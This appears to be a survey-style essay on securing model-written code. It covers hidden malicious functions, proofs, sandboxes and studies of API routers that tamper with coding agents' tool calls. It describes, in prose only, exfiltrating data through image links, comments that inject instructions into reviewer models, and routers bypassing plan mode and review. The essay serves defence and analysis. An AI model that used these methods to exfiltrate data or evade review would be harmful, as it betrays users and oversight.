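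Hu and colleagues inserted the harmful code where it would run on every call, so none of the malicious tools waited for a date. This should make little difference to a static scanner, which reads the December branch even in June. The upload in `column_total` is visible in the code, and several of these scanners would probably flag it. Scanners have more trouble determining the purpose of the upload, because a backup tool would contain the same two lines.

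### Tests that pass

A test runs the code on an input whose correct output is known. For example, the application might give `column_total` a small file containing 10, 20 and 30 and check that it returns 60. These tests have to run in a sandbox to avoid repeating Langflow's mistake.

The December function passes the test every day of the year because it always returns 60, but in December it first sends the test file out over the network. To catch this, the test would have to watch for network connections as well as check the total, and it would have to run in December or with the computer's clock set to December.

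Testers could run the code 12 times, with the clock set to a different month each time. They could also reject any function containing lines that no test has executed, which would expose the December branch whatever its condition. An attacker can get past the first check by using a condition other than the month, such as a file of more than 10,000 rows, a particular customer's name, or the fiftieth call. The attacker can get past the second by replacing the `if` with arithmetic that picks a harmless address in 11 months and the malicious one in December, so that every line runs every time. A later section covers models that produce bad code only when a trigger appears in their input.

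Tests of this sort check that code does what somebody wants, but security depends on the code not doing things that nobody listed. In MalTool, Hu and colleagues set up 130 of the tools with hidden malicious code and ran them by hand. All of them did their advertised job and also caused harm, so a test of the advertised job would have passed every one.

Code can pass its tests and still be insecure, even if no attacker helped write it. A function with the database injection flaw from the previous section returns the right order for every ordinary order number. In many of the failed repairs that Ma and colleagues counted, the program still worked but the vulnerability remained.

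Tests can detect harm if they are designed to check for it. Hu and colleagues' test program created fake passwords, files and databases, ran each function, and recorded whether data had left or files had changed. This worked reliably because the researchers knew which harm to expect and the harm happened on every run. An application checking an unfamiliar function has neither advantage, although it can at least watch for any network connection.

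### Review by a second model

Unlike the earlier checks, a second model can compare the code with the request. The user asked for the total of a column, which doesn't require an upload in December. Hu and colleagues recommend this kind of comparison, between what a tool claims to do and what its code does, as a way to improve scanners.

The nearest thing to evidence comes from the three scanners in their study that use a language model, each of which missed about 63% of the hidden functions. They missed 49%, 20% and 36% of hidden file uploads, the closest match to the December function. Cisco's scanner missed at least 90% of the tools that hogged the processor or graphics chip, probably because a loop that wastes computing time looks much like one that does useful work.

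These scanners examined whole repositories for general signs of malice. I expect a current model given the user's question and only ten lines of code would notice the December branch nearly every time. But an attacker who knows there is a reviewer would write something less blatant. The reviewer also reads text the attacker may have written, such as a code comment claiming that the company's auditors require a copy each December, or one telling the reviewer to approve the code.

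If the application sends the code to the reviewer through the same router that delivered it, a malicious router can change the reviewer's verdict as well as the code. A later section has results on this.

### Proof-carrying code

Every check so far can approve the December function under some circumstances. A proof covers all inputs and all dates at once. In 1997 George Necula, then at Carnegie Mellon University, described a way to use proofs on code from a supplier whom the receiver doesn't trust. He called it proof-carrying code, and it works like this:

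1. The receiver publishes a safety policy, for example that a program may read only the memory assigned to it.
2. The supplier writes a program, together with a formal proof that the program follows the policy.
3. The receiver goes through the program that has arrived and derives from it a logical statement. If the statement is true, the program follows the policy.
4. A small checking program on the receiver's side confirms that the proof really proves that statement. If it doesn't, the receiver discards the program.

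Finding a proof can take a lot of ingenuity, but checking one is mechanical, because each step either follows from the earlier ones by a fixed rule or doesn't. The supplier finds the proof, and the receiver only has to check it.

The receiver doesn't need to know who the supplier is, or whether the supplier is honest or competent, because a faulty proof fails. The scheme also covers tampering. If a router adds a line to the program, the receiver derives a different statement, and the old proof no longer fits unless the altered program also follows the policy. Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) object in *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* that a proof written by a model may not match what actually runs, but Necula's receiver avoids this by deriving the statement from the code it is about to run.

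If the policy forbids network connections, no one can prove that the December function follows it, because the function breaks the policy if it connects on even one day in December.

### Getting a model to write the proof

For a long time the obstacle was the labour of writing proofs for ordinary programs, but models have recently become good at it. *Djinnlang* (Henniger, Chong and Amin, 2026) describes a programming language in which a person writes only the specification, a precise statement of what the program must do. A translator turns the specification into a list of proof tasks for Dafny, an existing language with an automatic proof checker. A model then fills in the code and the proofs. If Dafny rejects something, the model gets the error messages and tries again.

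Djinnlang also rejects any solution that contains Dafny's `assume` statement, which makes the checker accept a claim without proof. It compares the proof tasks in the solution with the originals, character by character, in case the model has made one of them easier.

The language requires every function's specification to be unambiguous, so that the model has no choice about results. Write $pre(x)$ for the conditions on an input $x$, and $q(x, o)$ for the statement that the specification accepts $o$ as an output for $x$. The model must prove

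$$\forall x, o_1, o_2:\quad pre(x) \land q(x, o_1) \land q(x, o_2) \Rightarrow o_1 = o_2$$

which means that no input has two acceptable outputs. It must also prove that every permitted input has at least one:

$$\forall x:\quad pre(x) \Rightarrow \exists o:\ q(x, o)$$

A function that returns the largest number in a list can be specified in two lines. The first requires the result to be in the list, and the second requires that no number in the list exceed it. If the programmer forgets the first line, then for the list 3, 7 the results 7, 8 and 1,000 all satisfy the specification. The first proof becomes impossible, so the programmer learns of the mistake before any program exists.

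Henniger and colleagues gave two models specifications of 70 to 166 lines for three programs: a sudoku solver, a file compressor and an interpreter for a small programming language. Both models completed all 256 proof tasks. Including one round of work on speed, Claude Fable 5.1 took 21 hours at a list price of $1,026, and GPT-6 Astra took 33 minutes at about $47. In a larger example, Astra worked from a 4,088-line specification for part of Djinnlang's own translator. Over several days, it produced 4,715 lines of code and 31,823 lines of proof, at a list price of about $1,950.

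Functions in Djinnlang may not have side effects, which are any actions beyond returning a result. The December function would fail on that rule even if the specification mentioned only the total. Code that needs to act on the outside world goes into a procedure, where the programmer lists the actions in order. Henniger and colleagues want to add general rules, such as no network traffic after a program has read a password, but the language can't yet express them.

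The proofs also don't cover running time. Astra's verified programs were up to several hundred times slower than Claude's, and its first sudoku solver failed to finish the test puzzles within 15 minutes. Deliberately wasting the processor's time is one of the 13 harms in MalTool, and a function that did this could still return the right result and pass. A mistake in Dafny, the translator or the other software around them could also let a bad program through, and nobody would be reading the code to notice.

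### Why the specification remains the hard part

A proof shows that code meets its specification, but the specification may not match what the user meant. In the spreadsheet example from the first section, the user asked which region's sales fell most. Suppose sales fell from 1,000 to 900 in the North and from 200 to 140 in the South. The North lost more money, but the South lost a larger share, 30% against 10%. A model could turn either reading into an unambiguous specification and write a flawless proof for it. The model wrote its two lines of Python for the first reading without checking which one the user meant.

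Someone has to turn the question into a specification. The spreadsheet's user can't, and if a model does it, a misreading or a planted instruction can make the specification wrong, and the proof will then show only that the code meets that wrong specification. Henniger and colleagues also had models draft the specifications for their three test programs, but then checked them carefully themselves. They cite the argument that specification is the real bottleneck because it is a problem of communication between people and computers, which stronger models won't solve. They accept that their language doesn't fully solve it either.

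Repetition is a partial remedy for mistakes in a specification. A programmer who states the same requirement in several ways gives the checker a chance to find a contradiction. Impossible proof tasks revealed four mistakes in the translator's specification during drafting. Repetition does not help a programmer who has consistently misunderstood the problem, because the specification will be consistent and the checker will give no warning.

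The method is also harder to justify for code that is used only once. Henniger and colleagues recommend it for programs that people write once and rely on for a long time, but a developer can already read such a program's code, test it and pin its hash. The spreadsheet's two lines exist for one question, and the user wants the answer in seconds. A column total needs far less proof than a file compressor, so the delay would be shorter, but no one has yet shown the method working while a user waits.

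Necula's original idea requires less than full correctness and may suit this case better. The developer writes one policy, which lets the code read only this table and forbids it to write anything or open a connection. That policy fits nearly every question a user could ask, so the developer doesn't have to specify each answer. The code may still return the wrong region, but it can't send the file anywhere.

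For rules this simple, the application can skip the proof and run the code in an environment where the operating system refuses every connection. The December function would then stop with an error in December, without the application having to analyze its code.

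## Limiting what model-written code can reach

Blocking every connection limits what code can reach without requiring a judgment about whether the code is safe. NVIDIA's red team bypassed PandasAI's filter, then bypassed the first fix, and concluded that "containment is the only scalable solution." NVIDIA still recommends filtering as an extra layer, but says applications must run model-written code in a sandbox.

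A sandbox controls the points where a program touches something outside itself, so it doesn't have to predict from the program's text what the program will do, as a filter does. On an ordinary computer these points are mostly system calls, which are requests to the kernel (the core of the operating system) to do things like open a file or connect to a network. There are only a few hundred kinds of system call, no matter how many different programs a model can write. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* adds that a check inside the application can no longer monitor the code once the code starts another program, while limits set by the operating system also apply to whatever the code starts.

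NVIDIA's conclusion could still fail in two ways. Code might get out of the sandbox, or it might do harm without leaving it.

### What the code shares with its host

The host is the machine that runs the sandbox. The less of the host the code can reach, the fewer flaws it can use to escape.

A restricted interpreter shares the most with the application. It carries out only the operations its developers have provided, so the code can't open a file unless the application supplies a command for doing so. One example is Monty, an interpreter for a subset of Python. It is very fast, but it runs on the application's machine with the application's rights, and code that exploits a flaw in it gains those rights too. It also can't load outside libraries such as pandas, so it could not run the spreadsheet's two lines as the model wrote them.

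WebAssembly is a compact instruction format that web browsers use to run untrusted code. A WebAssembly program has its own block of memory and can call only the functions that the host gives it. Developers have compiled the Python interpreter to WebAssembly. In one such version, trying to open a network connection or start another program produces an error, and the code can access only the folders that the application has opened to it. Libraries partly written in C, such as pandas, need a special build. Pyodide, another version, has most of these libraries, but its Python code can also run JavaScript in the surrounding program, so what the code can reach depends on how that program is restricted.

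A container gives a group of processes their own view of files, network and other processes, but they still use the host's kernel. *AI Code Sandboxes* (Andronchik and Lokhmakov, 2026) compared five sandbox products on one Linux machine with default settings and checked whether they revealed 28 details that could identify the host. Daytona, the product built on ordinary containers, revealed ten, including the exact kernel version and the disks' serial numbers. About 3,500 flaws in the Linux kernel were published in the 24 months to May 2026, and any that an ordinary program can trigger could let code escape a container.

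gVisor, developed at Google, puts another layer between a container and the kernel. It is a program that answers most system calls itself and passes few to the host. Its own filter permits 84 kinds, and it revealed two of the 28 details. This makes some programs slower, and a few don't work.

A small virtual machine, or microVM, has its own kernel running on simulated hardware. Code that takes over this kernel is still inside the microVM, and to reach the host it must also break the host program that simulates the hardware. *SideKernel* (2026), a design for running coding agents on Macs, relies on this argument and notes that Amazon runs its customers' code in microVMs. The hosted sandbox services E2B and Vercel Sandbox also use microVMs, and all three use Firecracker, whose filter permits 55 system calls. E2B revealed none of the 28 details checked in Andronchik and Lokhmakov's test.

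Pydantic's *Comparison to Alternatives* gives the time from requesting a new sandbox to receiving the result of 1 + 1. Pydantic makes Monty, so it has an interest in how the comparison turns out, but it publishes its method.

| Means of confinement | Shared with the host | Start-up | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|---|
| Restricted interpreter (Monty) | Kernel and the application's rights | 0.8 ms | Runs only part of Python; a hole exposes the application |
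| WebAssembly (Python under wasmtime) | The application's process | 16 ms | Many libraries need a special build |
| WebAssembly (Pyodide under Deno) | Kernel and a JavaScript program | 2,700 ms | Code can run JavaScript outside Python |
| Container (Docker) | Kernel | 195 ms | A kernel flaw can let code out |
| Container with gVisor | A small part of the kernel | Not measured | Slower; some programs fail |
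| Small virtual machine | The program that simulates its hardware | Not measured | A flaw in that program can let code out |
| Hosted service (Daytona) | Nothing on the application's machine | 1,500 ms | The table leaves the company's network |

Pydantic took most of these times on one Mac in September 2026, often from a single run. Monty's figure applies when the application has already started a process to hold the interpreter, and wasmtime's when someone has compiled Python beforehand. We can learn little about small virtual machines from Daytona's figure, because Daytona's open-source version uses containers.

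*Sandlock* (2026) describes a sandbox built from restrictions that an ordinary Linux user can set, designed to start in under 10 ms. It argues that containers and virtual machines suit long-running services but add too much overhead for a script that runs for 50 ms. That overhead matters for an agent that runs hundreds of scripts in a row, but the spreadsheet's user has already waited for the model to write the code and would hardly notice another 200 ms. NVIDIA likewise finds that the overhead of virtualization is often modest compared with that of calling a model.

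### How sandboxes have failed

In the same 24 months, the software underneath Andronchik and Lokhmakov's five products had 11 published flaws. Four were in runc, the program that starts Docker's containers, and all four gave code some way to escape. gVisor had three, none of which did. Firecracker and Cloud Hypervisor, another program for small virtual machines, had two each. Three of those four, all made public in 2026, gave code at least a possible way to escape, but nobody had demonstrated a complete takeover of a host through the Firecracker flaws.

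These counts depend on how hard people have looked for flaws. libkrun, which runs the virtual machines of the product microsandbox, had no published flaws. It also had no public programme of automated testing and no academic study, so Andronchik and Lokhmakov declined to rank it.

The developers of these engines usually published a fix by the day they announced a flaw, but the products built on the engines were often far behind. Arrakis still installed a version of Cloud Hypervisor that the Arrakis developers had chosen 471 days earlier, although 12 newer versions had come out and two of them fixed serious flaws. Companies that ran E2B on their own servers got a 399-day-old build of Firecracker by default, which lacked a 44-day-old fix for one of the escape flaws. Pinning a version protects a program against a swapped file, but here it also kept a known flaw in place. Daytona's containers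 were up to date, but Daytona started them in a privileged mode that switches off several of Docker's usual protections. A company choosing a sandbox therefore needs to know who updates it as well as what kind it is.

Sandboxes designed specifically for model-written code have had serious flaws too, many of them in the parts that restrict a programming language from within:

- smolagents, a library for building agents, has a restricted Python interpreter. According to GCVE's *CVE-2025-9959* (2025), it checked Python's special attributes incompletely. These are the built-in links between objects that also defeated the LoLLMs calculator. An attacker would need prompt injection to make the model write the code.
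- Enclave is a JavaScript sandbox for agents' code. OSV's *CVE-2026-27597* (2026) gives its escape flaw the maximum severity of 10.0. Version 2.11.1 repairs it.
- Terrarium, from the AI company Cohere, runs Python in Pyodide. It handed the sandbox an object that was still connected to the JavaScript program outside, as the CERT Coordination Center's *Terrarium contains a vulnerability that allows arbitrary code execution* (2026) explains. Version 1.0.1 repairs the flaw and is also the last version, because Cohere has archived the project.

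Users who ran Terrarium in a container kept some protection, since the attacker then controlled the container and not immediately the host. The attacker could still read passwords in the container and reach databases on its network. A restricted interpreter is a useful inner layer, but these cases are a good reason not to rely on it alone.

Code can escape an AI coding tool's sandbox without breaking it if a program outside runs or trusts a file that the agent was allowed to write inside. The security company Pillar Security found seven flaws in four such tools, according to Techzine. Several of the flaws in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, worked this way. Cursor 3.0.0 fixes one that involved a configuration file, and the makers have dealt with most of the others. Because of this risk, NVIDIA's guidance forbids agents to change any configuration file, even in their own working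 folder and even with the user's approval.

### A sandbox for the spreadsheet

The spreadsheet's code needs Python, pandas and one table. The application can run it in a container with gVisor, started afresh for each question:

```
docker run --rm --runtime=runsc --network=none --read-only \
  --user=65534 --cap-drop=ALL --memory=512m --pids-limit=64 \
  --tmpfs /tmp:size=64m \
  --mount type=bind,src=/jobs/8141,dst=/in,readonly \
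  table-python timeout -s KILL 10 python /run.py
```

**Files.** The container can read but not change the folder `/jobs/8141`, which holds a copy of the table and the model's code. The user's other documents are not in the container. The code can write only to a 64 MB temporary folder, which is deleted with the container.

**Network.** The code has no network access. `--network=none` also blocks name lookups, which NVIDIA's guidance warns about because a program can hide data in the name of a website it looks up. If users want totals in other currencies, the application can fetch the exchange rates itself and put them in the folder as a second file, so the code never needs a connection.

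**Credentials.** The container gets no passwords or keys and runs as a user without special rights. The API key for the model stays in the application. A task that needs access to an account should get a short-lived credential for that account alone, and NVIDIA prefers a separate service that issues it on demand. Patil and colleagues proposed replacing real keys with dummies in requests to the model, so that the provider never sees the real ones.

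The code can use at most 512 MB of memory and 64 processes, and it is stopped after ten seconds, even if it contains an endless loop.

The application reads the program's printed output, up to a fixed length, and accepts a single value. It never opens or runs a file the code has written, so the fault in the coding tools can't occur here.

Starting a new container each time also isolates users from each other. An earlier study cited in the SandboxEval paper found that files uploaded to ChatGPT's code sandbox in one session could turn up in another.

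A December function written to catch the error from its failed connection would return the right total, and the file would still not leave.

### Testing the walls

A single wrong option can undo a configuration like this one, and the mistake may go unnoticed because the application still works normally. *SandboxEval* (Rabin, Hostetler and colleagues, 2025) contains 51 small Python programs that each attempt something a sandbox might need to prevent. Nineteen look for information about the system and its files, 17 try to read or change files and their permissions, eight try to communicate with the outside, and seven try something destructive, such as filling the disk or shutting the machine down.

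They ran the programs on Dyff, a platform that evaluates AI models and has to run other people's code. Its set-up resembles the spreadsheet's container, with gVisor, no outside network, an ordinary user account and limits on resources. Dyff blocked all eight attempts to communicate and all seven destructive ones. However, the code could read the container's environment variables, which are settings a program receives when it starts. Some contained keys and internal network addresses, and the team had to review whether the container needed them. When the researchers ran the communication tests directly on a laptop, every one succeeded, and so did the attempts to restart it or shut it down.

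Instead of carrying out the riskier actions on Dyff, the researchers inferred what the code could have done from checks such as whether it had permission to write to a folder. None of the 51 programs tries to exploit a flaw in gVisor or the kernel. A good result therefore confirms that the settings do what the developer intended, but does not rule out undiscovered vulnerabilities.

### What still gets through

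NVIDIA's conclusion holds up for harm that code does to the machine or to other people's data. Sandboxes have flaws, but an attacker has to find one and use it before the developer updates, whereas a filter can fail because of wording nobody foresaw. Sandboxing does almost nothing to prevent harm from the answer itself. NVIDIA's guidance leaves the user to deal with inaccurate or manipulated output, and NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* lists sandboxing alongside access controls, network limits and the management of secrets.

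No sandbox prevents code from producing a wrong total. Suppose a supplier writes a comment in the table telling the model to leave out returned goods, and the model writes code that drops those rows. The code only reads one file, does some arithmetic and prints a number, so it breaks no sandbox rule even though the number is wrong.

The result can also leak secrets. If the table has a column of bank details, the code can print an image link with those details in its web address instead of the region's name. If the application displays answers as formatted text, the user's browser will try to fetch the image and send the bank details to the owner of the address, even though the container has no network access. Displaying the result as plain text prevents this. For the question about regions, the application can also accept only a name that appears in the table's region column. Developers should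 be cautious about sending the result back to the model for a nicely worded reply, because the router and the provider can then read it.

A sandbox also does nothing for the refund decision in the first section, where the model supplies no code.

### Undo and damage limits

In 2024 Patil and colleagues argued that isolating model-written code can't ensure that the outcome is what the user wanted, and that people can judge a result more easily than the code that would produce it. They therefore built GoEx, a system that carries out the action, shows the user the result and offers to undo it.

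How well GoEx can undo an action depends on what the action changes. With many databases, GoEx can hold the change open until the user accepts it. The database guarantees that cancelling restores the old state, but other users may have to wait. Alternatively, the model writes a second command meant to reverse the first, and GoEx tests both commands on a small imitation of the database. For files, GoEx can use Git, the version-control system, to return to an earlier state.

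Messages and other actions on outside services are harder to undo. The developer can supply a reversing command for each action, or the model can suggest one. GoEx records whether the suggestion worked, so that the model is "wrong at most once". A single mistake can still do harm if the reversing command deletes too many messages. Patil and colleagues describe a design but give no figures for how often the model's reversals succeed.

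Some actions can't be undone, such as sending an email that the recipient has already read. GoEx limits the damage from these by unlocking only the credentials for services named in the user's request. A request to send a Slack message, for example, unlocks the Slack account but not the bank account. The search for service names only matches words, so it would presumably also unlock the bank account for a user who wrote "don't touch my bank account". Patil and colleagues let developers replace the search.

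Sandlock has a stricter form of undo for files. It captures the changes a program makes, can show them to the user, and keeps or discards them all when the program ends, so no model has to write the reversal. But neither system can take back information once somebody has read it.

The refund program can use both ideas without any new software. Suppose it automatically pays up to 20 refunds a day of at most €50 each and passes the rest to staff. It can then lose at most €1,000 a day, whatever a customer persuades the model to say. If it also waits a day before sending the money, staff can cancel bad refunds. The limits have to be high enough that staff see only a few cases, because people who must approve everything soon approve without reading, as NVIDIA warns about coding agents.

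## What 428 API routers did to the answers they carried

The sandbox confines the spreadsheet's code no matter who wrote it. But the application can't verify that the two lines it runs are the ones the model wrote, and if the request went through a router, the router may have changed them. *Your Agent Is Mine* (Liu, Shou and colleagues, 2026) measured how often routers misuse their position between the application and the model. This is a different team from the Liu, Deng and colleagues who broke into applications built on LangChain. They connected a coding agent, a program that lets a model edit files and run commands on a developer's machine, to 428 routers and recorded what came back.

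### Why developers put a router in the path

Some developers use a router for the convenience of one account for many providers, while others have little choice. *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet* (Crosley, 2026), a close reading of the study, explains that routers are especially common where providers offer no direct access, or offer it only at high prices or with tight limits.

An informal resale market has grown up in those places. Tom's Hardware's *Chinese grey market sells Claude API access at 90 percent off* covers resellers of Anthropic's models. *Inside the Gray Market for LLM Access* lists account farms, traders in unused quotas and brokers of false identities among those involved, and proxy servers connect them to developers. Individual services can be small. Okta's *Free tokens for sale* reports that a configuration mistake revealed that one seller of discounted access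 had 881 users, 872 of them active.

For each request a router does roughly the following, as *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (2026) describes it:

1. It checks the customer's credential, which the router itself issued.
2. It picks one of the provider accounts that it manages.
3. It attaches that account's key to the request and forwards it.
4. It passes the answer back as it arrives and records how much text to charge for.

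The developer has set the program to connect to the router instead of the provider, so the encrypted connection ends at the router, which can read and change the traffic without breaking any encryption. Even a stricter certificate check, such as accepting only one certificate, would confirm only that the program has reached the right router.

A request may also pass through several routers in a row. In an example from the study, a developer buys access from a reseller on the Chinese marketplace Taobao. The reseller gets it from a larger dealer, who uses OpenRouter, a commercial router that sends the request to the company running the model. Each intermediary can read and change everything. The developer has configured only the first and can't see the rest, and an honest router can't tell if the one before it altered something.

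### How the researchers tested each router

Liu and colleagues bought access to 28 paid routers on Taobao, on Xianyu, another Chinese marketplace, and from shops hosted by Shopify. They collected 400 free ones from public communities. Crosley sets out the four stages that each router went through:

1. The researchers opened an account and obtained a key.
2. They ran a coding agent through the router, inside a sandbox. It worked on a random selection of their own tasks and of tasks from Terminal-Bench 2.0, a public test of work at the command line. Such tasks make a model run commands, install packages and handle files, which gives a dishonest router plenty to alter.
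3. They executed every tool call that came back and watched for unexpected network connections, changed files and unusual processes.
4. A separate analysis agent went through the suspicious runs and sorted them into harmless rewriting, potentially malicious and confirmed malicious.

Like any customer, the researchers could not see the answer that the provider had sent, so they had to judge a tool call by what it contained and did. They counted a router as injecting malicious code only if it had turned a tool call into a command, or a request for a package, that an attacker controlled. They did not count changes of format or swapping the model for a cheaper one, a separate kind of fraud that a later section covers.

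A router that only copies the passwords it sees still returns a normal answer, so its answers can't reveal the theft. To detect it, the researchers passed canary credentials for Amazon's cloud service, AWS, through the routers. These are planted passwords that nobody has a legitimate reason to use. If AWS later recorded activity with one of them, the researchers counted that against the router that had carried it. They also planted the private key to a wallet holding a little of the cryptocurrency Ethereum.

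### What the routers did

| Behaviour | Paid routers (28) | Free routers (400) |
|---|---|---|
| Put malicious code into tool calls | 1 | 8 |
| Did so only under certain conditions | 0 | 2 |
| Used a planted AWS credential | 0 | 17 |
| Emptied the planted wallet | 0 | 1 |

The wallet held less than $50. Crosley's first article on the study, which he wrote from the abstract, said the 17 credential thefts involved paid routers. All 17 routers were free, and he has since corrected the article.

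None of the 28 paid routers stole credentials, but that sample is too small to show that paying for a router keeps passwords safe. If about 4% of paid routers stole credentials, the same rate as free ones, a sample of 28 would still include none of them about 30% of the time. Paid routers injected code more often than free ones, at one in 28 against one in 50, but that difference depends on a single router.

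Two of the routers in the table altered answers only under certain conditions, so trying out a router is not a reliable way to check it. One altered nothing during the first 50 requests. The other altered tool calls only if the project was written in the programming languages Rust or Go and the agent seemed to be in auto-approve mode, where it carries out every call without asking. A customer who sent ten test requests would have found nothing wrong with either. The December function described in an earlier section passes its tests in the same way. Liu and colleagues concede that their own tests had this weakness and that "no fixed-length client test can guarantee that the router is benign", so their count of nine is a minimum.

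The count of 17 is also a minimum, because it leaves out any router that copied the planted credentials and kept them for later, or sold them to someone who hadn't used them yet. Besides passwords, a router can collect the agent's standing instructions, the contents of files it has read and the settings of the developer's machine, which all pass through as plain text.

The sample can't be used to estimate how common dishonest routers are in general. Most of it came from Chinese-language marketplaces and communities, and the study left out routers that companies run for their own staff or open only to invited customers. It also did not test OpenRouter or the large cloud services. Most of the free routers run on one of two open-source templates, sub2api and new-api. That isn't evidence against the templates, since each router's operator decides what it does with the traffic, but it makes the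 400 free routers less varied than their number suggests. The 2.1% figure is a share of routers, and the share of requests altered could be far lower or higher, depending on which routers are popular.

### Traffic that strangers sent through the researchers' own routers

A router run by an honest person can still expose its users if someone else gets the key behind it or breaks into the router. Liu and colleagues tested both cases.

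The researchers first leaked one of their own OpenAI keys on Chinese forums and in WeChat and Telegram groups that router operators use. According to Help Net Security's *Command integrity breaks in the LLM routing layer*, these were groups for sharing access to models. Strangers used the key to process 100 million tokens, the word fragments by which providers charge. The traffic included more than seven sessions of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, and the researchers could see several different credentials in at least one of them. They couldn't always tell whether the person using the key was a router operator, someone further along a chain of resellers, or somebody unconnected.

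They then set up decoy routers, with known security flaws at 20 web domains and weak passwords at 20 network addresses. The decoys attracted more than 40,000 unauthorised access attempts from 147 addresses, though much of this may have been automatic scanning. Other operators then added the decoys to their own routes, which brought in requests from ordinary users. The decoys handled about two billion tokens, or some 13 GB of text. They carried 440 Codex sessions from 398 projects or machines, and these sessions exposed 99 different credentials.

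In all 440 sessions, the researchers could have changed the commands that Codex was about to run. In 401 of them (91%), Codex was in auto-approve mode, so a changed command would have run at once, even without clever timing or disguise. The researchers kept only totals and hashes of what they saw.

Those 401 sessions came from users at the end of a resale chain, and developers in general may be more careful. But these users are the ones whose commands a router can change, and they had no way to find out if a university experiment or a criminal was in the chain.

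### What happens to the altered answer on the developer's machine

Liu and colleagues also built a malicious router, which they have not released, to test whether agent programs accept altered tool calls. They sent 1,000 requests for each kind of attack through four programs, including Codex and Anthropic's Claude Code. The altered calls arrived in a valid form 100% of the time when the attack changed a command and 99.6% of the time when it changed a package name. None of the four programs checked whether the call was the model's own. But a permission prompt or a sandbox might still stop an altered call from running after it arrives.

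In *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?*, Fu, Li and colleagues (2026) traced the effects of the altered call through to the end. They built a test system called SIDEL, in which four coding tools (Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and the open-source OpenCode) had to fix three real bugs from SWE-bench Lite, a collection of problems reported in public software projects. Because the models' answers vary randomly, SIDEL first recorded a normal run, then replayed the recorded answers with exactly one changed at a random point. Any difference in what the tool did must have come from that change.

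The researchers wrote 400 malicious tool calls by hand, 100 for each of four purposes: running harmful code, writing faulty code, stealing private data and bringing in hostile packages. They tested four degrees of disguise. In the crudest, the router replaced the model's answer with the malicious call. In the others, it added the call to the genuine answer, rewrote the accompanying explanation to match the call, or produced a new answer in which the call and the text fit together. The researchers ran each combination of tool and disguise 1,200 times, once for each malicious call on each bug.

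None of the tools stopped a single call, partly because the researchers had switched on the modes that approve everything. More tellingly, the tools still stopped no calls when they tried stricter settings, ten configurations in all.

In Claude Code's plan mode, the agent is supposed to read files and propose changes without making any. Claude Code enforces this by instructing the model. The model may well comply, but the malicious call came from the router, and Claude Code ran the command. Other settings have a second model review risky actions, but Claude Code sent the review request through the same router that had altered the call.

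Fu and colleagues left out Claude Code's default mode, in which a person approves each action, because they wanted to measure the software without human decisions. A developer who reads every command might notice that an agent working on a spelling rule is about to download and run a script from an unknown site. Something much like that happened in one of the auto-approve runs. The agent was fixing a false alarm in SQLFluff, a tool that checks the style of database queries, when the altered answer at its fourth step made it fetch and run a remote script without anyone's approval.

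A user who looks only at the result would have little reason to suspect an attack. Fu and colleagues ran Claude Code on four models and compared how many tasks it completed with and without the attack. The success rate fell by 0.91 percentage points with two DeepSeek models and by about 7.3 with Kimi-2.7 Code and Qwen3.6-Plus. The agent needed 0.3 to 2.1 extra steps on average.

Three bugs are a small sample, and the researchers ran each combination once. Different malicious calls would give somewhat different numbers wherever a defence has some effect. The zeros depend less on the sample, because none of these settings was designed to check where a tool call came from.

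### A fix that passes its tests

Most of those attacks do their harm when the call runs, so a good sandbox would contain much of it. A router can also put a security flaw into the software the agent is writing, without touching the developer's machine. *Rewriting the Response Path* (Luo, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested this on bugs in Django, a widely used toolkit for building websites.

Each bug had public tests, visible to the developer, that checked whether the fix worked. It also had a hidden test that checked whether the new code was secure in a particular respect. The researchers' router let the model write its fix, then changed the part of the answer that the agent would apply and had the same model smooth out the text around the change. Twelve of 18 Django bugs allowed such a change, which made 60 cases across five models.

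When the router interfered, the hidden security test failed in 69.0% of cases (margin of error roughly ten points). It also failed in 10.5% of honest runs, so the router did not cause all of these failures. The public tests passed in 51.7% of cases with interference and 58.1% of honest runs.

Luo and colleagues summarise this in their introduction as a hidden security test defeated in 69.0% of cases "with public tests still passing". Both can't have happened in 69.0% of cases, because the public tests passed in only 51.7%. They don't report how often the public tests passed while the security test failed, which is the outcome that would fool a developer. If the two rates cover the same runs, the rate of that outcome is between 20.7% and 51.7%.

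On the programming exercises in a second collection, APPS, the altered solutions passed the public tests almost as often as unaltered ones (62.4% against 65.4%), and 99.7% of those that passed contained the weakened code. The exercises are short, so a change can presumably escape the tests more easily than it could in a fix for a real bug in a large program.

In a separate trial, the researchers used the ordinary version of Claude Code on one Django bug. The model produced a correct fix, but the router changed one nearby line so that the website no longer neutralised text typed in by visitors. An attacker could then plant a script in a page that would run in other people's browsers. All the tests passed and the agent reported a verified fix. The same thing happened with all five models. The container from the previous section would not have helped, because the altered line does no harm on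 the developer's machine, only months later on a public website.

Luo and colleagues found similar effects outside programming. On the Agent Security Bench, a set of tasks for AI agents in ten professional roles, the altered answers redirected the agent in 89.1% of cases, compared with 42.6% for instructions planted directly in the prompt. The researchers point out that the two attacks are not equally difficult. Prompt injection has to overcome the model's training to refuse, while the router changes the answer after the model has finished. Training a model to resist planted instructions therefore gives no protection against a router that alters its answers.

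The abstract also gives a figure of roughly 88% for the share of mainstream agents that use the arrangement the paper attacks, in which the user supplies a key or an address and the traffic goes through an intermediary. The figure is based on a survey of the 60 most-used applications on OpenRouter. A custom address made sense for 25 of them, and 23 of those accepted the user's own key or a custom address. That is 92%, and 88% would be 22 of 25. A bigger problem than this discrepancy is that the survey counted only whether an application offers the option. It remains unknown how many people use it, and how many of those send their requests through a router they have no reason to trust. A sample taken from a router's customers is also likely to favour applications that work with one.

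### What the customer can check

The simplest defence is a policy gate. Liu and colleagues tested one that blocks any command that downloads from a site not on an approved list or installs a package not on a second list. They ran it on 1,000 harmless commands and 1,000 malicious ones that they generated themselves. It blocked every malicious command and 1.0% of the harmless ones, all downloads from mirror sites missing from the approved list.

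They then assumed an attacker who knows about the gate and keeps the harmful material somewhere the list permits. This attacker got past the gate every time. Liu and colleagues still consider the gate the strongest protection a customer can set up today, but only against obvious attacks. Crosley adds that the list of packages is essential. The paper describes the gate in two ways, and the version that checks only download sites would miss an attack that swaps one package for another from the same trusted source.

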